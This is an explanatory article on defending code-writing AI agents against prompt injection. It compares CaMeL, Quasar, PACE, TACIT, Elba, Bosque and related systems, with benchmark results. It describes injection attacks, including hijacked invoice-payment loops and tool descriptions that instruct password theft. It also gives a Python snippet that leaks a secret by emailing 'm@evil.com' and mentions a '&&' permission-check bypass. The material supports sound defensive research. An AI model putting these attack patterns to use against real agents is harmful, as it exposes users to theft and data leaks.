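Anthropic's November 2025 post *Code execution with MCP* is the source of the most quoted figure, a drop from 150,000 tokens to 2,000, or 98.7%. The figure comes from an example, not a benchmark, and compares loading every tool description at the start with letting the agent open only the files it needs. An agent that makes JSON calls could save many of the same tokens with a search tool, which the post also suggests. Code separately saves tokens when data moves between tools. In another of Anthropic's examples,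 an agent copies a two-hour meeting's transcript from one service to another, and passing it through the model could add 50,000 tokens.

Cloudflare later published its own figure in Carey's *Code Mode*, which describes fitting an entire programming interface into 1,000 tokens. Tomé and Curry's *Code Mode* adds that this covers more than 2,500 operations through two tools. The 1,000 tokens include only the description the model receives at the start, not the tokens it then uses to search and write code.

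Some developers don't use MCP at all. Willison (2025) reports in *Code execution with MCP* that he found command-line tools more effective for coding agents. A shell needs few descriptions because models have already been trained on the common commands, but it also gives the agent access to every program and file that its user account can reach.

### What an ordinary language permits

Python can express harmful actions as easily as useful ones. If hidden text in an invoice takes control of the model, the model could write this:

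```python
for invoice in find_invoices():
    pay("GB66-9999", invoice.amount)
```

An agent that writes unrestricted Python could also delete files or upload passwords. Anthropic therefore warns that code actions require a secure sandbox (a closed environment for running code), with limits and monitoring that direct tool calls don't need. Cloudflare's sandbox has no internet access. Code in it can use only the tools it receives as objects called bindings, which work much like capabilities. The access keys stay outside the sandbox, so the code can't leak them.

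But an agent that pays invoices needs the binding for `pay`, so the sandbox would allow the loop above. To stop it, somebody has to specify which payments are acceptable as well as which tools the agent may use.

### CaMeL keeps the syntax and changes the interpreter

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in 2025, enforces such rules without asking the model to learn a new language. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that its designers chose a restricted form of Python because models write Python well. They then built their own interpreter, the program that runs the code. A simplified CaMeL plan for the invoice might look like this:

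```python
document = find_invoice("Acme")
details = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find the account number and amount",
    document, output_schema=Invoice)
pay(details.account, details.amount)
```

The system works in five steps:

1. A "privileged" model reads the user's request, but no invoices, and writes the plan.
2. The interpreter runs the first line and labels `document` as untrusted, because it came from outside.
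3. A "quarantined" model, which has no tools, reads the document and returns an account number and an amount in the required format.
4. The interpreter gives `details` the same untrusted label, because its contents came from `document`.
5. Before `pay` runs, a policy for that tool checks the labels on its arguments. If the account isn't trusted, the interpreter blocks the payment or asks the user.

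The separation of the two models comes from an earlier design by Willison. It prevents an injection in the invoice from adding a call, because the plan already exists when anything reads the invoice. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) point out in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* that the injection can still change the data passing through the plan. In their example, text in a calendar alters the schedule that an agent emails to the user's boss. In an invoice, a thief needs to change only the account number, so CaMeL also has to check labels.

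### What the policies cost

AgentDojo is a benchmark that gives agents office tasks and plants injections in the data they read. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, put CaMeL's completion rate on it at 67%. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, with its policies on and off. They compared it with Randori, an agent of their own that also labels data:

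| System | Model | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |

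The policies cut the share of completed tasks from about 70% to 37.5%. Sixteen tasks are a small sample, but Garby and colleagues also cite a test on AgentDojo's Slack tasks in which CaMeL with policies completed 7 of 21. Some banking tasks require the agent to read a bill from a file and pay it, which a strict policy forbids because the file is untrusted. A benchmark has no user who can approve an exception. In real use, CaMeL could finish more tasks by asking for approval, but it would interrupt people more often.

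Even without policies, only 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded. In about two thirds of the task-attack combinations, the attacker needed a tool call that the plan would never contain, so writing the plan before reading untrusted data was enough to stop the attack. The benchmark probably understates how useful the policies are, since a real attacker could target the data in a particular plan instead of using ready-made injections.

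Two of the five successes show how much even restricted Python can express. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that matched each instruction in the file to a tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose which tools the agent called.

Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies. However, it enforces only some of CaMeL's rules, and its plans may "endorse" certain untrusted data, marking it as acceptable before the agent has read it. This lets the model itself exempt data from the restrictions. Both successful attacks on Randori relied on endorsement. The user had asked the agent to make a payment according to a file's instructions, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Labels can't distinguish a forged invoice from a genuine one, and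 this case is also outside CaMeL's stated scope.

Randori's plans are written in LLMbda, a language that no model had seen in training. The models learned it from a syntax summary and error messages, and in this small test the unfamiliar language made no clear difference to success.

### Gaps in the labels

CaMeL's labels can also go wrong in ways that are hard to see in the code. Suppose `balance` is secret and a plan contains these lines, based on an example from Garby and colleagues:

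```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL would block an email sent directly inside `if balance > 10000`, because that call depends on a secret. Here, when the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to `False` and the interpreter labels it secret. The line `rich = False` then doesn't run, so `rich` never receives a label and the interpreter allows the email. When the balance is low, the program sends no email, so anyone who can see whether an email was sent learns whether the balance is above 10000. An interpreter that labels only the values it changes can't catch this leak, but a compiler can by examining both branches before the program runs.

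An attacker would need to get the privileged model to write that plan, which is harder than planting text in an invoice. Another fault they found could affect an ordinary plan. Putting an untrusted value inside a text string, as Python programmers often do, made it trusted, so `f"{details.account}"` could pass a check that `details.account` would fail.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) proves a related result in a formal model. It describes a plan that branches on an answer from the quarantined model. If the labels track data but not branches, an injected answer can decide which branch runs and so reveal a secret.

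Somebody also has to write and maintain the policies. Tallam and Miller, who work for a security company, warn that an organisation with hundreds of tools may end up with hundreds of inconsistent rules. They would replace CaMeL's Python with a small security language, because Python's dynamic types and exceptions make programs hard to analyse before they run.

### Quasar separates logic from actions

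*Quasar* (Mell, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) takes up that idea without making the model write the new language. It distinguishes internal code, such as loops and comparisons, from external calls that affect the world or consult another model. Engineers annotate each external call with its relevant effects, such as the resources it uses, and Quasar tracks those effects as the program runs.

Models struggled to write raw Quasar code, which consists of nested lists of numbered operations. They therefore write Python, limited mainly to function calls, local variables, `if` and `for`, and a compiler translates it into Quasar. Quasar variables can't change once they have a value, so the compiler has to restructure some code. For instance, it turns an `if` statement that may change a variable such as `found` into an expression that returns either the new value or the old one.

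Consider this program, in which both lookups are external calls:

```python
amount = get_invoice_amount("Acme")
budget = get_budget("office supplies")
if amount <= budget:
    pay_invoice("Acme")
```

A Python system that requires approval for every call would request it three times, once for each of the two lookups and once for the payment. Neither lookup needs the other's result, so Quasar requests approval for both together, runs them at the same time and requests approval again before the payment. The annotations must also record dependencies that the program doesn't show, such as a balance check that has to wait for a payment.

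Mell and colleagues measured these average savings:

| Tasks | Fewer requests for approval | Less running time |
|---|---|---|
| GQA, questions about images | 26% | 18% |
| AgentDojo | 26% | 27% |
| BrowseComp-Plus, questions that each come with about 100 documents | 97% | 93% |

About half of the GQA and AgentDojo programs had no approvals to combine. The BrowseComp-Plus programs made many calls to other models, most of which could run in parallel. Restricting agents to a subset of Python lowered accuracy only slightly, from 71.8% to 71.4% on GQA and from 64.5% to 63.4% on AgentDojo. The savings figures exclude programs that failed to compile or run.

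Fewer approval requests don't necessarily lead to better decisions. A person who has stopped reading single requests may not read a list of a hundred calls either, and rejecting any batch ends the program. The approval feature also doesn't record where an account number came from, so a user would have to notice the thief's number without help.

### Checks at the tool boundary

Other proposals leave the agent's code alone and check each call as it reaches a tool, so they can work with JSON calls as well as programs. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes that MCP require labels stating what a tool can do, how confidential its data is and whether anyone has verified its output. MCP currently has only optional hints. Developers could then write rules that block, require or allow a sequence of calls, or ask the user to confirm it.

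In an example from Doshi and colleagues that involves no attacker, a user adds a medical appointment to a calendar, and the agent moves a clashing work meeting and mentions the appointment in its email to a colleague. One rule would keep private details of an event out of emails to people who aren't attending it. Another would require an email to every attendee after each change. Doshi and colleagues checked such rules in a formal model but had not yet built the software to enforce them. The rules also depend on honest labelling, which a company can assume more safely with its own tools than with a stranger's.

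Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, argue that reviewing a tool before installing it can't be enough. Two email add-ons may have identical code but different written instructions, with one telling the model to use a fixed template and the other telling it to copy a password into the message. PACE therefore examines every call just before it runs. It traces whether protected data or untrusted text could have influenced the call, and compares the call's effects with what the user's request authorised.

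PACE had the lowest attack success rate, or tied for the lowest, in 76 of 79 comparisons across eight benchmarks and three families of models. Its task completion rate was at most three percentage points below an undefended agent's, a much smaller loss than CaMeL's in the banking test, though the benchmarks differ. But the version that Li and colleagues tested could restore some calls that one of its checks had proposed blocking, so their full guarantee applies only to a stricter version.

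Rules can also require calls to happen in a certain order. In *Soteria* (2026), an agent must call a check named `No-Flown` before it cancels a reservation, a rule that the booking system does not enforce. Soteria checks the plan for violations before it runs and again at each call. An equivalent rule for the invoice would require `get_order` before `pay`, although this alone wouldn't ensure that the plan compares the amounts.

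### When a subset looks like Python

A restricted language that looks like Python could repeat Solidity's problem, where familiar-looking code did something unexpected. The risk depends on how the interpreter handles code outside the supported subset of Python. If it either does what Python would do or stops, a programmer's wrong guess may cause delay but won't send money to the wrong place.

Monty, an interpreter from the software company Pydantic, mostly follows this rule. It runs AI-written code in a subset of Python, and the code can reach files and the network only through functions that the engineer supplies. Pydantic's *Monty* gives a start-up time of 0.8 milliseconds from a prepared pool, compared with 195 milliseconds for a container, the usual kind of sandbox. According to Pydantic's *Python language / parser*, a program that uses an unsupported construct, such as `yield` or `del`,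 fails before any of it runs, with a message that names the construct. Willison (2026), in *pydantic-monty investigation*, an AI-assisted review, also found that unsupported features generally fail cleanly.

Some differences produce no error, however. Pydantic's *Limitations* lists one that could matter in a payment program:

```python
class Approval:
    def __init__(self, granted):
        self.granted = granted
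    def __bool__(self):
        return self.granted

if Approval(False):
    pay(account, amount)
```

Python calls `__bool__` to decide whether an object counts as true, so it would not make the payment, but Monty ignores `__bool__` and treats every such object as true, so it would. This is the same kind of trap as Solidity's wrapping numbers. Models probably seldom define classes in short code actions, and Pydantic documents the difference, but nothing would prompt a model to check the documentation if it writes code as it would for standard Python. Monty could remove the danger by rejecting code that defines `__bool__`, as it already does with `yield`.

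Error messages can help a lot, but only when there is an error to report. When Mell and colleagues sent the Quasar compiler's messages back to the model, the share of AgentDojo programs that ran without errors rose from 83% to 89%. Accuracy rose from 63.4% to 67.7%, which was higher than with ordinary Python.

Sending runtime errors back to the model is riskier. A program may pay an invoice and then fail on the next line, and a model that tries again may pay twice. The error message may also contain text from an untrusted document, which could carry a prompt injection to the model that writes the plans. CaMeL censors its error messages to limit this, but its retry loop runs outside the part of the system that tracks labels. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker who can see whether a policy blocked each attempt learns one bit per attempt, so enough attempts could reveal a whole secret.

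Randori avoids both problems by having the model test and revise its program in a simulated bank with invented data. The program runs on the real accounts only once it works in the simulation. Quasar's compiler messages are safe because they depend only on the program's text and arrive before any tool has run.

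## Action languages whose compiler rejects unsafe actions

Ordinary Python code does not mark which data is secret or which functions could leak it, so CaMeL has to track labels on data while a program runs. Several researchers instead want agents to write in languages that record this kind of information, so that software can reject an unsafe program before it runs.

### How TACIT keeps a secret

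Odersky and colleagues, at the Swiss university EPFL, built a system of this kind called TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types). It is an MCP server, so existing agents can connect to it without modification. The agent sends TACIT short Scala programs, which the standard Scala 3 compiler checks. The programs can reach files, commands and the network only through TACIT's library.

TACIT relies on capture checking, the experimental Scala extension that lists a function's capabilities in its type. If `f` is a capability for writing to a file, the function `s => f.write(s)` takes text, uses `f` and returns an empty value, so its type is `String ->{f} Unit`. A function of type `String -> Unit` uses no capabilities, so it is pure.

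Suppose an agent has to process a confidential contract. TACIT gives it the text inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can work on the text only through the wrapper's `map` method, which applies a function to the contents and wraps the result again. The compiler accepts this program:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
  val contract = readClassified("/contracts/secret/acme.txt")
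  val length = contract.map(text => text.length)
  println(length)
}
```

The user sees the length on the terminal, while the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. TACIT separates the two outputs because everything a hosted model reads goes to the company that runs it.

The next program tries to copy the contract into an ordinary file, which the agent could then read:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
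  val contract = readClassified("/contracts/secret/acme.txt")
  val report = access("/contracts/public/report.txt")
  contract.map(text => report.write(text))
}
```

The compiler rejects the fourth line because `map` accepts only pure functions. The function passed to it uses `report`, so its type is `String ->{report} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. According to the error message, `report` "cannot flow into capture set {}", where the empty braces mean that the function may use no capabilities.

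The agent can still have the contract summarised. TACIT's `chat` function sends wrapped text to a second model that the user trusts, such as one running on the user's own computer, and wraps the answer. The agent can then save the summary in a confidential file without reading it.

The purity rule also prevents the leak that CaMeL's labels missed, in which a program sent an email only if a secret balance was above 10000. A program can test a `Classified` balance only inside `map`, where it cannot send email.

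### Permissions that end with a block

In both programs, `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one folder, which lasts until the closing brace. An agent might try to keep it for longer:

```scala
val readLater = requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
  () => access("/contracts/plan.txt").read()
}
```

The block returns a function that would read the file when called. The compiler rejects the program because the function's type refers to a capability that exists only inside the block. Network access and external commands work the same way, with a list of permitted hosts or command names.

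TACIT makes some checks at run time rather than compile time. Its types do not record which folder a path belongs to, so a program that asks for a file outside `/contracts` compiles, but the library stops it when it runs.

When the compiler rejects a program, none of it has run, so the model can correct it and try again without repeating an action such as paying an invoice. *LACUNA*, which describes a later system from the same group, gives the example of code that subtracts 50 from a balance and then returns text where the caller needs a number. In Python, the subtraction would happen before the error appeared, but the Scala compiler rejects the code before either line runs.

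Agents have to write their code in Scala's safe mode, which forbids features that can bypass the compiler's checks. These include unchecked type casts, which tell the compiler to treat a value as another type, and reflection, which finds and calls code by name while a program runs. Either could make the compiler lose track of a capability. Library authors can still use these features in a module marked `@assumeSafe`, but they then have to verify the module themselves, as programmers do with `unsafe` blocks in Rust.

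### Tests against attacks

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a small software project with a folder of access keys and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections and added 11 trials in which the user asked for secrets, sometimes while posing as someone with authority. That made 131 trials per model. They ran each trial twice, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with them as plain text.

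| Model and measure | Secrets wrapped | Secrets in plain text |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6: trials without a leak | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5: trials without a leak | 100% | 91.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6: ordinary tasks completed | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5: ordinary tasks completed | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 trials, both involving a false claim of authority. MiniMax leaked them in 11, 8 of which involved direct or deceptive requests from the user. Odersky and colleagues note that Sonnet without the wrapper often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection, so the wrapper probably did not make Sonnet better at the tasks themselves.

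Taken alone, 131 trials without a leak are consistent with a leak rate of up to about 2%. The reasoning behind TACIT's types is stronger evidence, since it also covers untested programs. The trials mainly test whether the software enforces those types as intended.

On AgentDojo, only one of about 1,900 attacks on TACIT succeeded, and it did little harm. In that attack, an injected hotel review recommended a different hotel, and the agent booked the right one but quoted the review to the user. With the model o4-mini, TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in all four areas, including 53% against 81% for office work, although Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's completion rates comparable to CaMeL's published results.

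### The effect on ordinary work

To find out whether writing Scala makes agents less capable, Odersky and colleagues used τ²-bench, in which an agent deals with simulated customers. They ran each task ten times with ordinary tool calls and ten times with Scala programs:

| Model | Airline: tool calls | Airline: Scala | Retail: tool calls | Retail: Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
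| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Scores rose by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of the programs needed a retry, and those usually compiled after one or two more attempts. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software repairs, MiniMax's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%, or five fewer repairs.

Odersky and colleagues credit the gains to structured results and compiler messages. But a Scala program can also combine several calls, which helped models in the CodeAct experiments, where they wrote Python. The test didn't compare Scala with Python code actions, so it can't show whether types helped. It does suggest that writing a fairly unfamiliar language did little harm.

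*LACUNA* reports a larger loss in performance. Its system goes further than TACIT because the typed code that the model writes also controls the agent's next steps. On 392 customer-service tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with this system and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. The paper describes the results as "on par", which is hard to reconcile with a 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the programs in the retail tasks, and 89% of those that a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote in the telecoms tasks.

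The results may differ because LACUNA's code has to do more, and because the models ran with reasoning turned off. The paper also suggests the models had seen less Scala than Python. An agent with a strict action language stays within its permissions even when it writes bad code, but it may get little work done.

### A similar system in Haskell

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents a similar system, Elba, in which agents write Haskell. Haskell already separates pure functions from actions, so Elba can use existing security libraries. An engineer can also define a new kind of action that includes only approved operations.

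One example is an agent that compiles bibliographies. Every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The function that fetches an entry from DBLP returns it with the type `Trusted Bib`, and the function that writes to the bibliography accepts only that type. The agent can sort and filter entries with ordinary code, but it cannot itself create a `Trusted Bib`, so a program that writes an invented entry does not compile.

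In 100 tasks, none of Elba's 925 citations was incorrect, while an ordinary agent with web search got details wrong in 19 of its 1,002. Part of the difference may come from Elba's direct access to DBLP. The technique could also help with the forged Acme invoice, where the danger is a false account number. If `pay` accepted only a `Trusted Account`, and only a lookup in the company's own supplier records returned one, an agent could not pay an account number copied from the invoice.

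Zhou and colleagues also tested Elba on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with four recent models. The agents completed 14 to 18 tasks without security policies and 8 to 10 with them. CaMeL completed 4 to 6 with its own policies. Elba took about three times as long as CaMeL because it calls the model again as new data arrives.

All four models resisted every one of the benchmark's 105 attacks even without policies. This supports the objection that better models make such languages unnecessary. Zhou and colleagues reply that attacks are improving too, and cite an automated attacker from OpenAI that consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. They therefore ran a harsher test in which they altered Elba so that any sub-agent that read an injection received the attacker's text as its instructions. Each model made 735 runs with policies and 735 without:

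| Model | Attacks stopped, with policies | Attacks stopped, without | Tasks completed, with policies | Tasks completed, without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT-5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

The policies stopped every attack but reduced the number of completed tasks by a third or more. The test shows how much damage a successful injection could do, but not how often one would succeed. The compiler ensured that programs used the security library, but stopping every attack also required the library to check the origin of the data as each program ran.

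The models had little trouble with Haskell itself, needing an average of 0.1 retries per call and running out of retries in only 7 of 2,688 runs. These models are newer than those in the LACUNA test, so the two results do not show that Haskell is easier for models than Scala.

### Bosque puts conditions on each call

Zhou and colleagues adapted an existing language, but Mark Marron designed a new one, Bosque, to make code easier for people, models and automatic checkers to reason about. Marron (2026) extends Bosque to agents in *Toward an Agentic Infused Software Ecosystem*. Much of Bosque looks like TypeScript, but it has no loops. To check that every amount in a list is positive, for example, a programmer writes `amounts.allOf(pred(x) => x > 0i)`.

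Loops are hard for automatic checkers because proving something about a loop usually requires finding a statement that stays true on every pass. Bosque has no loops, so its checker can translate most code directly into logical formulas and send them to a solver. A model that writes a loop, as it would in a more familiar language, should get an error message rather than a program that behaves unexpectedly.

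A Bosque interface also states when an agent may call each operation and what the operation may use. This is a shortened version of Marron's payment example, with most of the names changed:

```text
api pay(amount: USD, from: Account, to: Account)
  env = { LIMIT: USD }
  permissions = { \account:${from.number}\ }
  requires 0.0<USD> < amount;
  requires amount <= env.LIMIT ||
           $events.contains(Approve(|payee=to, sum=amount|));
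```

The `env` line lists the information the operation needs from its surroundings, and `permissions` limits the operation to the payer's account. The `requires` lines are preconditions, like those in SPARK. The amount must be positive, and it must either be within the limit or have the user's approval recorded in a log that agents cannot alter.

Suppose an agent has to pay Tom half of a lunch bill. Its program uses a language model to read Tom's message and work out the amount, then calls `pay`. The model could return any amount, such as $1,000 if Tom jokingly asks for that much. The checker reports that the amount may exceed the limit and that the program has not obtained approval. The agent can then add a request for approval before anything runs. The run-time system checks the same conditions and stops any unsafe call that reaches it.

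These conditions would not stop a payment to a thief's account if the amount were within the limit. The checker also limits the length of text and lists in order to guarantee an answer, so it could miss an error that appears only with longer input.

There is little evidence yet on how well agents work in Bosque. A blog post by Bosque's developers mentions "rough experimentation" in which Gemini 2.5 was about 20% more successful with a Bosque payment interface than with its TypeScript equivalent. *Trustworthy-by-Construction Agentic APIs* (Marron, 2025), a research proposal, reports that feedback from the checker raised agents' success within three attempts by over 20%. Neither source gives the number of tasks. The proposal also reports that the checker took at most 1.4 seconds to examine each of three programs of up to 1,800 lines.

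The 2026 paper reports no tests of agents using the new payment rules. Experimental versions of the software are public, and Marron is still combining them into a system for general use. He expects even very capable agents to benefit, because expert programmers do and a 1% chance of deleting a customer database would still be too high.

### Plans that come with a proof

In *Guardians of the Agents*, Erik Meijer, who helped design LINQ, proposes requiring an agent to prove that a plan is safe before carrying it out. Checking a proof can be easy even when finding it is hard, so the user would not have to trust the model that wrote it. Java similarly verifies compiled code before running it.

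In Meijer's examples, the model writes its plan as a list of steps in JSON before it reads any emails or files, much as in CaMeL. A separate checker then compares the plan with written rules. One rule could forbid the contents of an email from reaching an address outside the company by any path. The checker would reject a plan that forwards a summary of an email to such an address, whether the idea came from the user or from a dishonest tool description.

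Writing complete rules is difficult, as another of Meijer's examples shows. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the agent plans to delete `*.txt`, which means every text file in the folder. Suppose the rule for the task is:

after the plan, `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` do not exist.

The agent's plan satisfies this rule, so a correct checker would approve it. Somebody also has to write:

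after the plan, every other file that existed before still exists.

With the second rule, the checker rejects the plan. People take this rule for granted, and so may forget to write it down.

Models can now write long proofs in Lean, so for many plans, producing the proof may be easier than deciding what to prove. Meijer acknowledges that nobody had formally measured how writing a whole plan first affects an agent's success. The article presents a design and examples but no experiment. Zhou and colleagues list an open-source checker, published by Nada Amin and others in 2026, that is based on Meijer's proposal.

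Other new agent languages, such as Garby and colleagues' LLMbda, are also at an early stage. Meijer designed Universalis for office workers to read, but according to Marron, it was neither public nor formally described in early 2026. Odersky and colleagues chose an existing language partly because a new one would need a lot of investment before people could easily read and edit it, and before models had enough human-written examples to learn from.

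### Who has to learn the types

An agent doesn't need a course in Scala, but someone has to write instructions for it. For AgentDojo, Odersky and colleagues gave the model about 170 lines on how to use TACIT, along with a list of functions. Some of these lines warn about pitfalls. For example, if a function inside `map` fails, TACIT hides the error message because it might contain secret text. The program then appears to have worked, but the user sees an empty result. Odersky and colleagues therefore instruct the model to return a message such as "No matching transaction" instead of raising an error.

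Engineers have more to learn. TACIT's reusable library has about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new area of work, such as airline bookings, needs a few hundred more to describe its functions and data. They replace JSON descriptions of similar length. A company with ten such areas, at 300 lines each, would need 4,000 lines of Scala, 3,000 of which would replace JSON it had to write anyway. Agents can help write the descriptions, which people then review.

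The engineers also decide what counts as secret. In the banking interface, `getBalance()` returns an ordinary number, while `readFile` returns `Classified[String]`. If a company wanted to hide its balance from the model's provider, returning it as an ordinary number would be a mistake that the compiler couldn't detect.

Small differences in notation can also matter a great deal. This line from the library makes `map` safe:

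```scala
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

In ordinary Scala, programmers write function types with `=>`. If an engineer used it here out of habit, `map` would accept functions that write files or use the network, and the compiler would no longer reject the program that copied the contract. An experienced Scala programmer might miss the error because `=>` looks normal.

Reviewers also have to notice such mistakes, though they can concentrate on the interface instead of reading every program an agent writes. Odersky and colleagues consider their typed interfaces simple and readable, but they did not test this on reviewers. An easy test would be to give people interfaces with a few wrong types and count how many they find. Until someone does this, it is uncertain whether a company without Scala programmers could safely maintain its own version of the library.

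### Sandboxes, permission requests and early users

Most companies would find it easier to put their agents in a sandbox. Sandboxes work with any language and need no typed interfaces, and production systems already use them. They can also restrict programs that TACIT's compiler never checks. The external-command example in TACIT's documentation permits `pip` and `python`, but Scala's rules don't apply to a Python program started this way. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

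However, a sandbox that grants a permission allows both harmless and harmful uses of it. If an agent may read a contract and contact its model's provider, it can send the contract to the provider without leaving the sandbox. `Classified` prevents this by restricting what can be done with the contract's text.

Companies can also ask users to approve risky actions, but people stop reading the requests. Fonseca quotes Anthropic's figure that users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of these requests are probably harmless, so the figure doesn't show how many bad ones people accept. Automatic permission rules can also fail. Zhou and colleagues describe a fault, reported in March 2026, in which Claude Code checked only the first of several commands joined with `&&`.

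*Safe Scala an introduction*, by VirtusLab, a software company that works with EPFL, recommends combining compile-time checks with a sandbox. The compiler can prevent leaks through permitted operations, and the sandbox can limit the damage if the compiler, the library or an external command fails. Neither prevents every leak. For example, a pure function could take longer to finish when a secret balance is above 10000, and an agent that measured the delay would learn whether the balance is above that amount.

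TACIT has few known users so far. The Scala Days talk *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* introduces CapybaraClaw, an agent that EPFL and VirtusLab are building on TACIT and intend for production use. Another session at the conference, *Lets build a personalised agent harness in Safe Scala*, invites programmers to build an agent whose only tool runs Scala code. Both come from people who already use Scala, and neither shows that a company relies on TACIT. According to VirtusLab, safe mode is available only in the compiler's nightly builds, test versions that many companies would hesitate to use for an agent that handles payments.
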